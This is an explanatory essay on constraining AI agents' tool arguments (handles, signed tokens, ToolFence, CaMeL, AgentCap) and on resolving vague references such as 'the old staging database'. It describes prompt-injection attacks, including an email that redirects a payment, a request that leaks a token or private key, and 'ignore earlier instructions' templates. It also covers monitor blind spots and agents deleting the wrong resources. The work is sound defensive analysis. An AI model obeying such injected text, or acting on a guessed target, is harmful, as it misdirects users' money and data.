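In response, Railway's *Changelog #0288* (2026) announced on 1 May that volumes deleted through the programming interface would stay recoverable for 48 hours, as volumes deleted on the website already did. This gives the owner time to notice and undo a mistake, but it doesn't reduce the agent's authority. Abdelwahab also recommends Railway's own MCP server, which uses short-lived tokens and lets users choose which projects an agent can access. He claims that its fixed set of tools makes it impossible for an agent to go rogue, but an agent with access to a project could still use a permitted tool on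 the wrong resource in it.

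## Binding authority to an agent's tool arguments

A language model writes the arguments of a tool call as text, so an argument such as a payee or a record ID names a resource but carries no right to it. The right comes from the credential that the harness attaches. Suppose Lena's assistant can also make payments, and she asks it to pay BillPay, her electricity company, $100. The model should write:

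`send_money("BillPay", 100)`

During the task, the assistant reads an email with a hidden instruction to pay someone else, and the model writes this instead:

`send_money("Mallory", 100)`

Many harnesses use an allowlist of the tools that the model may use for a task. Including `send_money` in the list admits both calls, but leaving it out prevents Lena from paying her bill. Li, Cao and Xiao (2026), in *ToolFence*, call this attack within-tool hijacking, because the attacker keeps the tool that the user expects and changes only a sensitive argument. Checking the arguments' format doesn't help either, since "Mallory" and "BillPay" are both well formed.

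*tool_use Is Not invoke()* (Das, 2026) points out that the harness normally "invokes whatever name and arguments the model printed". Das proposes that the harness compute a digest (a short fingerprint) of the arguments when it approves a call, compute it again just before running the call, and refuse if the two differ. Each approval works once and covers one call, so approving a search doesn't approve a payment that the model requested in the same message. This is an individual's untested proposal to the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which publishes internet standards. The check prevents an approved payment to BillPay from becoming a payment to Mallory, but something still has to work out which payee Lena authorised, and there are at least four ways to do that.

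### Keeping the handles in the harness

The harness can hold the handles itself and show the model only labels for them. Lena's payment would then work like this:

1. Before the model starts, the harness creates a handle for each payee that the task may involve. Each handle can pay only one account.
2. The harness stores the handles in a table that the model cannot change, and tells the model that `payee-1` means BillPay.
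3. The model writes `send_money("payee-1", 100)`.
4. The harness looks up `payee-1`, finds the handle and uses it to make the payment. If the label isn't in the table, the harness returns an error.

The email can still give the model Mallory's account number, and the model can still write it in a tool call, but the table has no entry for it. Unix file descriptors work the same way.

The bank doesn't have to change anything, because a handle can be a small function in the harness that always pays BillPay's account, like the `readTemplate` function that could read only one file. The harness still holds Lena's full banking credential, so a flaw in the harness would expose her whole account.

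A label is still a name, so the protection depends on what the harness puts in the table. If the table lists all 60 of Lena's past payees, the email can redirect the payment to any of them. The email can also change the amount unless each handle has a limit. A tool such as `add_payee`, which creates an entry for any account the model supplies, would remove the protection.

Zagidulin and Caballero support the general idea, arguing that a more deterministic component outside the agent should hold the agent's keys and use them on its behalf. But neither evaluation described below tests label substitution, so the case for it rests mostly on experience with operating systems.

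### Tokens that fix the arguments

A table inside Lena's harness is no help to a payment service that wants to check her authorisation for itself. Niyikiza (2026), in *Attenuating Authorization Tokens for Agentic Delegation Chains*, proposes a signed token that lists the tools an agent may call and the argument values it may use. For Lena's monthly bills, the central part of the token might be:

```json
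{
  "send_money": {
    "recipient": {
      "constraint_type": "one_of",
      "values": ["BillPay", "WaterCo", "CityRent"]
    },
    "amount": { "constraint_type": "range", "max": 500 }
  }
}
```

The constraint types in Niyikiza's March version include an exact value, a list of permitted values and a numeric range. If a token constrains any of a tool's arguments, the service must reject a call that contains an argument the token doesn't mention. Otherwise a call with the permitted recipient could add an argument that charges a different account.

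Lena's assistant might pass the electricity bill to a sub-agent, a second agent that does part of the work. The sub-agent doesn't need to pay the other two companies, so the assistant derives a narrower token:

```json
{
  "send_money": {
    "recipient": { "constraint_type": "exact", "value": "BillPay" },
    "amount": { "constraint_type": "range", "max": 100 }
  }
}
```

The assistant can do this offline, without contacting the server that issued the original token:

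1. The assistant signs the new token with its own private key. The new token contains the sub-agent's public key and a hash of the original token, which ties the two together.
2. To make the payment, the sub-agent presents both tokens, along with a fresh proof that it signs with its own private key. The proof covers the tool and the exact arguments.
3. The payment service checks the original token's signature using the issuer's public key. It then checks that the holder of the original token signed the new one, and that the new token adds no tools, loosens no constraints and expires no later.
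4. The service checks the arguments against the narrower token.

A payment to Mallory fails at step 4. The sub-agent can't give itself a broader token either, because the service would reject it at step 3.

Some older token formats, such as macaroons, also allow offline narrowing. Every service that verifies a macaroon needs the secret key that creates it, according to IETF's *Agent Delegation Chain* (2026), a separate draft intended to be merged with Niyikiza's approach. In Niyikiza's design, a service needs only a public key, so it can check tokens without being able to issue them.

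The tokens don't limit how often an agent uses them. For payments, the service must record which proofs it has accepted, so that a thief can't reuse a copied one. But the sub-agent can still sign a second proof and pay the same bill twice. Niyikiza leaves that problem to other controls, such as rate limits. The service must also ensure that "BillPay" refers to the right account.

None of this is a standard yet. Niyikiza submitted the current draft as an individual on 15 June 2026, and it expires on 17 December unless a new version replaces it. Niyikiza has asked the IETF's OAuth mailing list whether the problem is within the working group's scope. Formal verification of the narrowing rules is unfinished. Niyikiza's company, Tenuo, has a reference implementation with tests of those rules, but the tests don't measure how well agents do their work or resist attacks.

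### A plan made before the agent reads anything

ToolFence, the system that Li and colleagues built, decides what Lena authorised before her assistant reads any email. It handles the payment in these steps:

1. A separate model receives only Lena's request and a list of tools that the operator has reviewed. It writes a plan that permits one call to `send_money`, with BillPay as the recipient and 100 as the amount.
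2. The assistant starts work as usual. It can read any email, including the attacker's.
3. When the assistant proposes a call, an ordinary program called the monitor compares it with the plan. It checks the tool, the stage of the task, the arguments and how many uses remain.
4. The monitor reserves the single use before it lets the payment go ahead. If it later confirms that the payment didn't happen, it restores the use. If it can't find out, it keeps the use reserved.

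A payment to Mallory fails at step 3 because the monitor records the email's contents as data, which cannot add anything to the plan. A second payment to BillPay also fails because no uses remain.

Lena might instead ask the assistant to pay the bill in `march.pdf`. The recipient isn't known in advance, so the planning model specifies that it must come from a particular field in the output of the tool that reads that file. The assistant can choose arguments that don't affect anyone's authority, such as a note to the payee. An email that mentions Mallory still can't redirect the payment, because her name didn't come from the file. But if an attacker can edit `march.pdf` to put Mallory's name in that field, the monitor will accept her as the recipient.

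The plan may also omit a step that the task needs. For example, Lena might ask the assistant to reply to an email and attach a file from her drive, and the assistant might have to search the drive first. If the plan has no entry for the search, a second isolated model reviews the proposed call and can add a permission for it. The assistant must then propose the call again, and the monitor checks it as usual.

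### Tracking where each value came from

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues presented in 2025, also plans from the trusted request, but it replaces the agent's usual loop with a program. As Li and colleagues describe it, a privileged model plans the work and a quarantined model processes the untrusted text. For the bill in `march.pdf`, the program could look roughly like this:

```
bill = read_file("march.pdf")
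payee = extract(bill, "account to pay")
send_money(payee, 100)
```

The privileged model writes these lines from Lena's request. The quarantined model carries out `extract`, so it processes the bill but doesn't control what the program does next. An interpreter runs the program and tags each value with where it came from and who may read it. Before `send_money` runs, the interpreter checks the tags on `payee` against a policy. The policy might accept a payee from a file Lena named and refuse one from an email.

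This is close to the provenance tracking that Rajani and colleagues proposed in 2016. The tags that CaMeL calls "capabilities" describe data, whereas a capability in ToolFence is permission to make a particular kind of call.

The tags don't show whether a value is true. If the attacker has replaced the account number in `march.pdf`, the tag listing `march.pdf` as the number's source will be correct, and a policy that trusts the file will allow the payment.

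### Signed tokens with a hand-written policy

The system in *AgentCap* combines short-lived tokens, tracking of sources and a policy that people write in advance. Its example rule for payments sets these main conditions:

| Condition | What the rule demands |
|---|---|
| Declared intent | paying a bill or sending a payment |
| Agent's trust score | 0.8 or higher |
| Permission already held | reading the account balance |
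| Protected argument | the recipient, which must have support in a trusted source |

When Lena's assistant proposes the payment, it also declares an intent, such as `pay_bill`. AgentCap's policy engine checks that the assistant has already obtained permission to read the balance. Because the recipient is a protected argument, the engine also checks where the recipient's name has appeared. It accepts BillPay because the name is in Lena's request, even if some emails mention it too, but refuses Mallory, whose name appears only in an email. If every check passes, the engine signs a token valid for 30 seconds and one call, and a separate gateway checks the token before forwarding the payment.

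The declared intent gives little protection by itself, because a model that follows the attacker's instructions can also declare `pay_bill`. The example rule doesn't protect the amount, so it wouldn't stop a payment of $9,000 to BillPay.

The token also doesn't fix the recipient. It records the action and the resource, but the resource in this rule, `bank_account/transfers`, covers every transfer. The engine checks the recipient when it issues the token, so the harness has to send the gateway the same arguments that the engine approved. A digest like the one Das proposes, stored in the token, would let the gateway confirm that the arguments match.

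AgentCap also gives each agent a trust score and lowers it after every refusal. By default the score starts at 0.8, the minimum for `send_money`, and one refusal reduces it to 0.56. Each normal call then closes 1% of the gap between the score and 1, so the assistant would need 79 normal calls before it could pay anyone. An attacker who provoked a single refusal could therefore block Lena's real payment. The test results show no such collapse in trust, so the problem may arise only with these settings.

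### What the tests found

The main benchmark for these systems, AgentDojo, gives agents everyday tasks in simulated banking, travel, chat and office software, and hides attackers' instructions in the data the agents read. InjecAgent tests similar attacks. AgentLAB spreads an attack over many steps, so that the harmful call looks like a natural part of the task.

Li and colleagues tested ToolFence and reran CaMeL for comparison, while AgentCap's developers tested their own system. In the table, attack success is the share of attempts in which the attacker's action took place. Each pair of figures gives the percentage without the defence, then with it. The last column gives the drop in task success, in percentage points, that the defence caused when there was no attack.

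| Defence | Benchmark | Model | Attack success | Task success under attack | Loss without attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| ToolFence | AgentDojo | Qwen3-max | 21.2 → 0.0 | 55.2 → 62.1 | 2.0 |
| ToolFence | AgentDojo | Llama3.3-70B | 15.5 → 0.0 | 47.7 → 55.2 | 2.3 |
| ToolFence | AgentLAB | Qwen3-max | 76.3 → 29.4 | 35.1 → 50.3 | 1.3 |
| CaMeL | AgentDojo | Qwen3-max | 21.2 → 0.0 | 55.2 → 45.2 | 23.2 |
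| CaMeL | AgentDojo | Llama3.3-70B | 15.5 → 0.0 | 47.7 → 39.3 | 22.7 |
| CaMeL | AgentLAB | Qwen3-max | 76.3 → 35.2 | 35.1 → 32.3 | 22.3 |
| AgentCap | AgentDojo | GPT-4o | 45.6 → 5.1 | 73.6 → 74.9 | 3.1 |
| AgentCap | AgentDojo | GPT-5.4 | 33.2 → 0.0 | 75.7 → 75.0 | 7.2 |
| AgentCap | InjecAgent | GPT-4o | 23.2 → 8.6 | 74.1 → 62.2 | 11.7 |
| AgentCap | InjecAgent | GPT-5.4 | 12.0 → 0.0 | 73.0 → 65.4 | 5.9 |

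The ToolFence and AgentCap rows can't be compared with each other, even where both used AgentDojo, because the models and attacks differ. Li and colleagues averaged results for six phrasings of the injected instructions over 609 pairs of tasks and attacks, while the AgentCap evaluation used 949 attacked tasks. Without a defence, attacks succeeded more than twice as often against GPT-4o as against Qwen3-max.

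The ToolFence and CaMeL rows are easier to compare because they share models and attacks, but Li and colleagues had an interest in the result. They ran both of CaMeL's roles on the model under test so that CaMeL would not have a stronger helper, while ToolFence always used GPT-4.1-mini to write and review its plans. Small differences may also mean little. On AgentDojo, CaMeL completed slightly more tasks under attack than without one, which could be due to noise or the different mix of tasks. ToolFence's two-point loss is about the same size as that gain.

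The attack success rate of zero applies only to the attacks in that test. The six AgentDojo phrasings are general templates, such as telling the model to ignore its earlier instructions, and a real attacker could study the defence and design an attack against it. ToolFence did much worse on AgentLAB, where a group of agents had refined each attack beforehand. Despite ToolFence, those attacks succeeded 29.4% of the time with Qwen3-max and 38.3% with Llama3.3-70B.

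In a separate test with Llama3.3-70B, Li and colleagues removed parts of ToolFence one at a time. They used Agent Security Bench, which places instructions in tool results and in the agent's stored memory. Attacks succeeded 45.4% of the time with no defence, 24.0% with ToolFence but without its argument checks, and 5.1% with all of ToolFence. The other checks therefore stopped about half of the attacks that would have succeeded, and adding the argument checks stopped most of the rest. The argument checks lowered task success by less than one percentage point.

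Li and colleagues also measured what each check adds, using 285 proposed calls that the user had not authorised. Checking the tool alone stopped only 31, and checking the source of the arguments stopped another 23. Restricting calls to the right stage of the task stopped 113 more, as did limiting how many times a permission could be used. We can infer little about real attacks from these proportions, because the researchers had added many calls that came at the wrong stage or reused a spent permission.

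The five remaining calls all came from one task, in which the simulated user gave the attacker's account number as a "new landlord's". Since the number was in the trusted request, its origin gave ToolFence no reason to refuse it. Any system that relies on where a value came from has this limit, so a fraudster who persuades Lena to type in an account number doesn't need to deceive her assistant.

On 200 AgentDojo instances with Qwen3-max, the average time rose from 6.3 seconds to 10.3 with ToolFence and 81.7 with CaMeL. Li and colleagues attribute CaMeL's delay to its repeated model calls to write and run code. In *AgentCap*, the median time to issue a token is 67 microseconds, and verifying one takes 80. Those figures cover only AgentCap's own checks, so they can't be compared with the whole-task times for ToolFence and CaMeL.

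AgentCap's remaining failures with GPT-4o fall into three groups. In some, the attacker only wanted the model to write a particular reply, which checks on tool calls can't stop. In others, the policy didn't list the argument the attacker changed. In the rest, the attacker's value came through a field that nobody had marked as untrusted.

### Who issues the authority

A monitor that strictly enforces a plan will also enforce a bad one. In ToolFence, a model writes the plan, so the system's security depends on that model understanding Lena's request. Li and colleagues limit the damage in two ways. The planning model never sees untrusted text, and the operator's list of reviewed tools determines which arguments are sensitive, so the model can't classify a payment's recipient as non-sensitive.

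The model that approves missing steps is more exposed, because it reviews calls that the assistant proposed after reading untrusted text. Li and colleagues found that an attacker can spread instructions over several records until a harmful call looks necessary, and the reviewer may then grant too much authority. They could have removed the reviewer, but task success under attack on Agent Security Bench fell from 44.3% to 35.8% without it, which is lower than with no defence.

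People can write the policy instead, as they did for AgentCap. Its developers read the benchmark's task descriptions before writing the rules, though they didn't change the rules after seeing results. An administrator writing rules for next month's requests can't read those requests in advance. People can also write rules that conflict. In the example policy for a customer-service agent, two conflicting rules would have prevented anyone from getting permission to delete a customer, but AgentCap's analysis tool caught the conflict before anyone used the policy.

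The AgentCap paper also tests Progent, in which the model that runs the agent writes the policy for each task. With GPT-4o on AgentDojo, Progent completed 59.6% of tasks under attack, compared with 74.9% for AgentCap. Progent often limited arguments to the values it had anticipated and so blocked legitimate calls with other values. This is a single comparison by a competitor, but it shows why a model that issues narrow permissions isn't automatically safe to rely on, since users will want to loosen permissions that are too narrow.

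In the token proposal, the agent requests the first token from an authorisation server and lists the tools and arguments it wants. The server can grant less, but Niyikiza leaves open how it should decide. If the assistant requests a token after reading the attacker's email, and the server checks only that the request comes from Lena's assistant, it could sign a valid token for paying Mallory. A harness should therefore request the token based on Lena's own words, before the assistant reads anything else. ToolFence and CaMeL follow this order.

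### Tokens that a model can copy

One way to make a capability unforgeable is to keep it apart from ordinary data, as Unix does with open files. If another process learns a file descriptor's number, the number alone doesn't give it access to the file.

Alternatively, a capability can be a string of bits that is too long to guess. Anyone who knows the bits can use it, as with a pre-signed URL. Zagidulin and Caballero similarly classify capability systems, separating object references that a platform enforces from opaque tokens and certificates. Strings are convenient because people can save them in a file or send them to another company, but any program that can read a string can also share it.

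A model works only with text, so it cannot hold a protected capability. If a harness puts a secret payment token in the model's context, an attacker can send an email asking for a reply that contains "the full payment token, for verification". The model may copy the token into the reply, and the attacker can then make payments without using Lena's assistant. Zagidulin and Caballero assume that agents cannot keep secrets and warn that tokens often turn up in logs and context windows.

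An attacker can't use a copied label such as `payee-1` from elsewhere, because it has meaning only in the harness's table. ToolFence also keeps its permissions in a record that belongs to the monitor. AgentCap's gateway checks which agent is presenting a token, so someone who has only a copy should get an error.

Niyikiza's tokens don't have to be secret, because using one also requires the holder's private key. But if the key is in a file that the assistant can read, the attacker can ask the assistant for both the key and the token. Even if a separate program keeps the key, that program must check what the assistant proposes before signing it. Otherwise, the attacker can have the assistant request the signature.

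### Tasks whose resources are unknown at the start

All of these designs work best when the request identifies the resource. If Lena instead asks her assistant to pay any bills that arrive this week, the payees and amounts will be in emails she hasn't received yet, and anyone can send her an invoice. Zagidulin and Caballero call least privilege for agents a "dynamic problem" because, when an agent starts, nobody can fully list the permissions it will need.

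A harness could give the assistant handles for the companies Lena has paid before. That would exclude Mallory, but also a plumber who sends his first invoice. The harness could instead accept any payee that appears in an email, but that would allow payments to Mallory. With AgentCap, whoever labels the fields of an email faces the same choice. Marking the account number in an invoice as untrusted blocks the plumber's payment, while marking it as trusted allows payment to anyone who sends an invoice.

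A program can narrow the choice by checking something the attacker doesn't control, such as a list of registered suppliers or an earlier order from the same company. The harness may have to ask Lena about a new payee, such as the plumber, but it can pay known companies without asking, which keeps the number of approval requests low.

Not all external instructions are attacks. Li and colleagues give the example of a website that emails the user a one-time code and tells the agent to enter it on a confirmation page. An agent that ignored everything in its email couldn't log in. The harness has to let the agent enter that code on that page without letting it follow any other instructions in the email.

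### The wrong handle among the right ones

Suppose Lena also asks the assistant to pay her rent, so it rightly holds handles for both BillPay and CityRent, but it sends the electricity payment to CityRent. The label is in the table, a token that covers both companies permits the call, and both names come from her request. A list of permitted payees would not catch the error, but a plan that ties each payee to its own amount would, unless the two amounts were the same. An attacker could cause this mistake, but it can also happen without one. Niyikiza acknowledges that an agent "can still be steered within its scope" if its token covers more than one resource, and recommends making each token as narrow as the task allows.

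## Turning a user's words into particular resources

Ana, a developer, tells an agent to "delete the old staging database". Her company has three databases that could fit:

| Database | ID | Created | Last used | Owner |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `staging-2024` | `db-118` | March 2024 | yesterday | payments team |
| `staging-old` | `db-204` | May 2025 | 3 months ago | Ana's team |
| `orders-stg` | `db-097` | January 2023 | 8 months ago | Ana's team |

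`orders-stg` is the oldest, `staging-old` has "old" in its name, and the year in `staging-2024` makes it look out of date. A handle or a token that fixes the tool's arguments could restrict the agent to one of these databases, but somebody must first decide which one Ana means. If the harness creates a handle for the wrong database, every later check will enforce that mistake.

Broad authority makes the mistake hard to notice. If the agent's token covers the whole account, deleting any of the three databases returns the same success message. There is no attacker, and Ana may be entitled to delete all three, so the database service has no basis for rejecting the request. If the token covered only her team's databases, trying to delete `staging-2024` would produce an error, but the agent could still choose wrongly between the other two.

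### Agents that picked the closest match

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, about its coding agent, describes several cases adapted from the company's internal log of its agents' misbehaviour. In one, a user said "cancel my job". The agent searched a computing cluster, picked the job with the most similar name and tried to delete it, although it could have been someone else's. In another, a user asked an agent to "clean up old branches" (separate lines of work in a code project). The agent listed the branches on the shared server and issued a command to delete those that matched a pattern, but the user may have meant only the copies on their own machine.

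Anthropic chose these cases to illustrate what its software should block, so they don't show how common such errors are. The log also records an agent that did delete branches from a server after misinterpreting an instruction. The agent that deleted PocketOS's database made a similar error when it assumed the volume belonged to staging.

The agent in the first case had a good reason to ask, because there was no exact match and it needed the closest one.

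### Resolving a reference step by step

A harness can make wrong guesses rarer and easier to catch by handling each reference in six steps:

1. List the candidates among the resources that the task may touch.
2. Compare them, using what the user said and the context.
3. Act, ask the user or refuse.
4. Show the user the chosen resource, with details that distinguish it from the other candidates.
5. Bind the choice to a stable identifier or a handle.
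6. Use that binding for the rest of the task.

Ordinary code should produce the list of candidates by querying the database service, because a model may leave some out or invent others. Limiting the list to resources the task is allowed to access rules out some errors. If Ana's task concerns only her team's staging databases, the harness can exclude `staging-2024` and every production database before the model chooses. The search also has to be complete, because an agent that reads only the first page of results may find one match and not notice that the user's words also fit others.

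In the second step, the word "old" favours `staging-old`. But if Ana said an hour ago that her team had moved its order tests elsewhere, that favours `orders-stg`. Evidence from text that other people can edit deserves less weight, since any of them could change a database's description to "old, safe to delete".

The agent can act if one candidate is clear enough for the action at hand. If several remain plausible, it may have to ask the user which one they meant. It should refuse if nothing fits or the only match is outside the task.

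A question such as "Delete the old staging database?" repeats Ana's words, so she would say yes whichever database the agent was about to delete. A better question would be "Delete `staging-old` (created May 2025, last used 3 months ago) or `orders-stg` (created January 2023, last used 8 months ago)?" Listing the owner wouldn't help her tell them apart, since her team owns both. The harness should take these details from the databases' records, because a model could describe one database and then delete another.

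Suppose Ana chooses `staging-old`. The harness records its ID, `db-204`, because somebody could rename the database or create another with the same name. It can also create a handle that permits deleting `db-204` and nothing else.

From then on, the agent should use the database's ID rather than reinterpret her words. Suppose it deletes the database, but the connection fails before the success message arrives, so it tries again. If it searches for "the old staging database" again, it finds only `orders-stg` among her team's databases, which now seems to fit, and deletes that too. If it uses the ID, the second attempt returns a "not found" error.

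Ana might not answer until the next morning, and by then a colleague may have started using `staging-old`. Just before the deletion, the harness can compare the database's current record with the details it showed her, and ask again if they differ.

### When a question is worth asking

A simple rule is to ask when the chance of error multiplied by its cost exceeds the cost of the question:

p × L > c

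The agent should ask the user when pL > c, where p is the chance that its best guess is wrong, L is the loss if it is, and c is the loss from interrupting the user. Suppose the agent has a 10% chance of choosing the wrong database, L is 10,000 units for a wrong deletion, and c is 5 units. The expected loss from deleting without asking is 0.1 × 10,000 = 1,000 units, so the agent should ask. If Ana only wants to know how large the old staging database is, L might be 1 unit. The expected loss is then 0.1 units, so the agent should answer and mention which database it looked at.

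With these figures, asking before the deletion is worthwhile if the chance of error is above 5 / 10,000, or 1 in 2,000. Asking before the lookup is never worthwhile, because even a wrong guess is less of a burden than the question.

The harm from an error depends partly on whether anyone can undo it. If the provider keeps deleted databases for 48 hours and restoring one counts as a loss of 20 units, the expected loss falls to 2 units. The agent can then delete `staging-old` and tell Ana what it did, but this works only if she notices a mistake within the 48 hours.

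Sometimes nobody can tell the agent which database the user meant. If deleting the right one would save 50 units in storage fees, the agent should delete nothing, because waiting loses at most 50 units while guessing has an expected loss of 1,000.

Pu, Lee and colleagues (2026) describe a similar rule in *LHAW*, a benchmark of long tasks with missing information. Their ideal agent asks when the expected value of the information outweighs the interruption, the delay and the loss of the user's trust. They measured how much each question helped, but left estimating the value of the user's time to future work. *Uncertainty-Aware Clarification in LLM Agents with Information Gain* (2026) adds that a question should be likely to improve the agent's use of its tools. By that test, asking Ana why she wants the database gone is worthwhile only if her answer would help identify the database.

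### Why a model's stated confidence may mislead

The easiest way for the harness to estimate the chance of error is to prompt the model for a confidence estimate. If the model reports 99.99%, the expected loss appears to be 1 unit, and the agent deletes the database without asking for confirmation. But if models are wrong 10% of the time when they report 99.99%, the true expected loss is 1,000 units.

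To be 95% confident that the error rate is below 1 in 2,000, a team would need to observe about 6,000 similar choices with no mistakes.

Two studies give reason to expect overconfidence. *When and How Should an Agent Clarify?* (Li, Wu and Meng, 2026) reports that models given incomplete questions often commit to one interpretation and confidently give wrong answers. Pu and colleagues found that vague phrases such as "the file" often led agents to make confident but incorrect assumptions, and that an agent might be more likely to notice a gap if the detail were missing altogether. "The old staging database" is this kind of phrase because it sounds complete. Both findings concern wrong guesses, not stated percentages, so they don't show how far off a model's figure is likely to be.

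Anthropic withholds the agent's own messages from the program that checks its commands, so that the agent can't get approval by claiming that a target "is definitely agent-owned". The program doesn't receive search results either, so if the user never named a particular job, it can't determine whether the agent found the job's ID in a search or made it up. A harness that keeps its own list of candidates can check this.

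The harness can also use the list for a cruder test than the model's confidence, asking the user whenever an action is irreversible and more than one candidate remains after the first step. This will produce some unnecessary questions, but ordinary code can count the candidates, and the model can't override the result.

### What happens when agents can ask

Researchers usually study this by removing information from tasks that agents can normally do and supplying a simulated user who knows what is missing. *Ambig-SWE* (Vijayvargiya, Zhou and colleagues, 2025) used 500 real bug reports. Agents received the full report, a vague summary, or the summary and a simulated user they had to question. Asking questions helped all six models. It let Claude Sonnet 4 fix 89% as many bugs as it fixed with the full reports, while the figure for Llama 3.1 70B was 54%.

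In a second experiment, asking was optional, and most models judged poorly when to ask. When the instructions said only that it could ask if anything was unclear, Claude Sonnet 4 asked no questions on 44% of the summaries and asked needlessly on 8% of the full reports. Qwen 3 Coder never asked, even when told that questions were critical to success. Llama 3.1, told to check carefully that it had all the information it needed, asked questions on 95% of the reports that were already complete. Vijayvargiya and colleagues counted only questions in the first three turns, so an agent that explored the code first and asked later would count as not asking.

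Pu and colleagues tested newer models on 285 incomplete versions of tasks from three benchmarks. GPT-5.2 asked a question in 97% of its attempts at one set of tool-using tasks, while Gemini 3 Flash never asked one on a set of coding tasks. Claude Opus 4.5 had solved all of the tool-using tasks when the instructions were complete. With incomplete instructions, it solved 47% with nobody to ask and 78% with a simulated user, counting a task as solved if at least one of three attempts succeeded.

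How often agents ask questions depends heavily on how researchers set up the test. On incomplete tasks from a simulated company, Pu and colleagues found that GPT-5.2 asked in 87% of attempts, Claude Sonnet 4.5 in 79% and Gemini 3 Flash in 32%. *Ask Early, Ask Late, Ask Right* (2026), which used the same collection of tasks, reports 52%, 23% and zero. In the second study, agents asked their first question on average 43% to 50% of the way through their actions, by which time they could already have deleted something.

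Asking more questions doesn't necessarily produce better results. *Asking What Matters* (2026) describes a model trained to ask about coding tasks, which matched GPT-5's success while asking an average of 3.0 questions, compared with GPT-5's 5.1. It did so by favouring questions that were relevant to the task and that a user could answer.

### When the target is vague

In many of these tests, the missing information concerned what to build or how it should behave. Ji, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Coding Agents Are Guessing*, instead varied how clearly the instructions identified the target. They took 69 routine software-team tasks, such as deleting a stale branch or rolling back a release, and wrote 32 different instructions for each. Some instructions identified one object by its full name, while the vaguest used phrases like "the old one", which fitted several. The files, tools and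 correct action stayed the same across each task's instructions.

Agents often guessed. Even with the vaguest targets, they acted in 36.4% to 81.3% of runs, depending on the model and harness. Among runs in which they acted, the share that made only the intended change fell from 67.9% with fully named targets to 8.6% with the vaguest, while the share that affected a wrong target rose from 9.6% to 75.1%.

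The next table gives results for all the instructions together, as percentages of all runs. OpenCode, Claude Code and Codex are the harnesses.

| Harness and model | Asked the user | Made only the intended change | Affected a wrong target |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenCode, Claude Haiku 4.5 | 38.3 | 19.8 | 15.8 |
| OpenCode, Codex-5.1-mini | 10.5 | 25.3 | 20.3 |
| OpenCode, DeepSeek-v4 | 1.7 | 36.8 | 31.8 |
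| Claude Code, Claude Haiku 4.5 | 44.5 | 21.4 | 13.1 |
| Codex, Codex-5.1-mini | 31.8 | 15.5 | 24.3 |

DeepSeek-v4 rarely asked questions, and it had both the most successes and the most wrong targets. A benchmark that counted only completed tasks would rank it first. Codex-5.1-mini asked questions three times as often in the Codex harness as in OpenCode. Ji and colleagues suspect this is because Codex offers a specific tool for asking them.

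Agents asked more often as the target became vaguer, but they hardly responded to the size of the possible damage. They acted in 65.5% of runs when a mistake would stay contained and in 64.0% when it would affect shared or production systems. Under the rule for asking, they should have become much more cautious. Pu and colleagues found that Claude Sonnet 4.5 did respond to the burden a question would place on the user. It asked 266 questions when told that the user was waiting to answer, but only 124 when the user was described as a busy executive. The models and tasks differed, but together the results suggest that a designer shouldn't rely on the model to weigh the harm of an error against the burden of a question.

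According to the paper's abstract, 55.8% to 67.8% of runs crossed at least one boundary, either by affecting a wrong target or by doing more than the task required. That range covers only runs in which the agent acted, and the share of all runs is 27.0% to 46.3%. Ji and colleagues switched off confirmation and simulated some services, so the figures can't be used to predict how often such accidents happen where people approve risky commands.

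### Failures after the question

Agents can also mishandle the answer. *AppWorld-UL* (Chen, Trivedi and colleagues, 2026) tested agents on 516 everyday tasks in simulated apps. For example, a user might ask an agent to return "the shirt I bought last week" after buying several. The best agent, which used Claude Opus 4.7, succeeded on 50.0% of the tasks with this kind of ambiguity and 48.6% of all tasks.

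An agent using GPT-5.5 completed 78.1% of the tasks when Chen and colleagues put the missing answers in its instructions, but only 12.8% when the simulated user wouldn't tell it anything. It scored 41.8% in the normal test, where it also had to ask every necessary question to pass a task, so that score isn't strictly comparable with the other two. On failed tasks, agents had asked only 37% to 40% of the necessary questions.

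Some errors happened after the user had answered correctly. Agents that asked several things at once sometimes matched an answer to the wrong question, and others forgot part of the original request. A harness could prevent mismatched answers if it asked about one resource at a time and itself stored the chosen ID.

*AM-Bench* (Huang, Li et al., 2026) tested five recent models in four harnesses, in 20,160 runs. Average success fell from 76.5% with complete instructions to 27.8% when the context was ambiguous, for instance about which data source to use. GPT-5.6 Sol and GPT-5.6 Luna did best with complete instructions but came fourth and fifth on average when something was vague or missing, so doing better on clear tasks doesn't guarantee doing better on unclear ones.

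In three of the harnesses, agents asked for clarification in 8.5% to 10.7% of the runs with incomplete instructions, and in the fourth they asked in 26.6%. Nobody answered, so Huang and colleagues estimated the benefit of asking by replacing the results of runs where agents asked with results from runs with complete instructions. For ambiguous context, the estimated success rate rose only to 34.4%, largely because agents had asked so rarely.

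When the instructions left out restrictions, such as which data was off limits, agents finished 77.5% of their runs, but every finished run broke at least one of the omitted restrictions. This is a good reason for the harness itself to restrict the list of candidates, though it may be unfair to blame an agent for breaking a rule it never saw.

### Why people approve the wrong thing

A confirmation prompt helps only if the user reads it. Anthropic first reported that users accepted 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts, and later put the figure at 97% in *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026).

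A careful person would approve a long series of harmless commands, so a high approval rate doesn't prove that people are careless. Anthropic got better evidence from a controlled test. It hired 1,053 testers for a coding study and, once in each session, replaced a permission prompt with one for a clearly dangerous command. 13.6% of the testers rejected it. The rejection rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

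The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than most users. Anthropic also published these results to justify replacing most prompts with an automated check, which blocked 89% of the same commands. Still, users may find the wrong database even harder to spot than a clearly dangerous command, because they did ask the agent to delete a database.

If Ana caught a wrong choice as often as the testers caught the dangerous command, a confirmation prompt would reduce a 10% chance of wrong deletion to about 8.6%, and the expected loss from 1,000 units to 864. The prompt would still be worth its 5 units, but most of the risk would remain. The 5 units also don't include the harm from unnecessary prompts, each of which makes people less likely to read the next one.

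Users reject 39% of the plans that Claude Code presents for approval, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. They may reject a plan because they want a different approach, so the difference doesn't show that they would notice a wrong resource, but it suggests that they pay more attention to some questions than others. A harness should therefore ask rarely and, when several candidates remain, present a choice, because Ana can't choose between `staging-old` and `orders-stg` by pressing "yes" out of habit.

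### Letting the user pick

Ana could avoid the problem by selecting the database from a list when she writes her request. Her choice would identify the resource, as picking a file in a save dialog does, and the harness would receive an ID that no model had to guess. Ji and colleagues consider naming the exact resource the easiest precaution a user can take.

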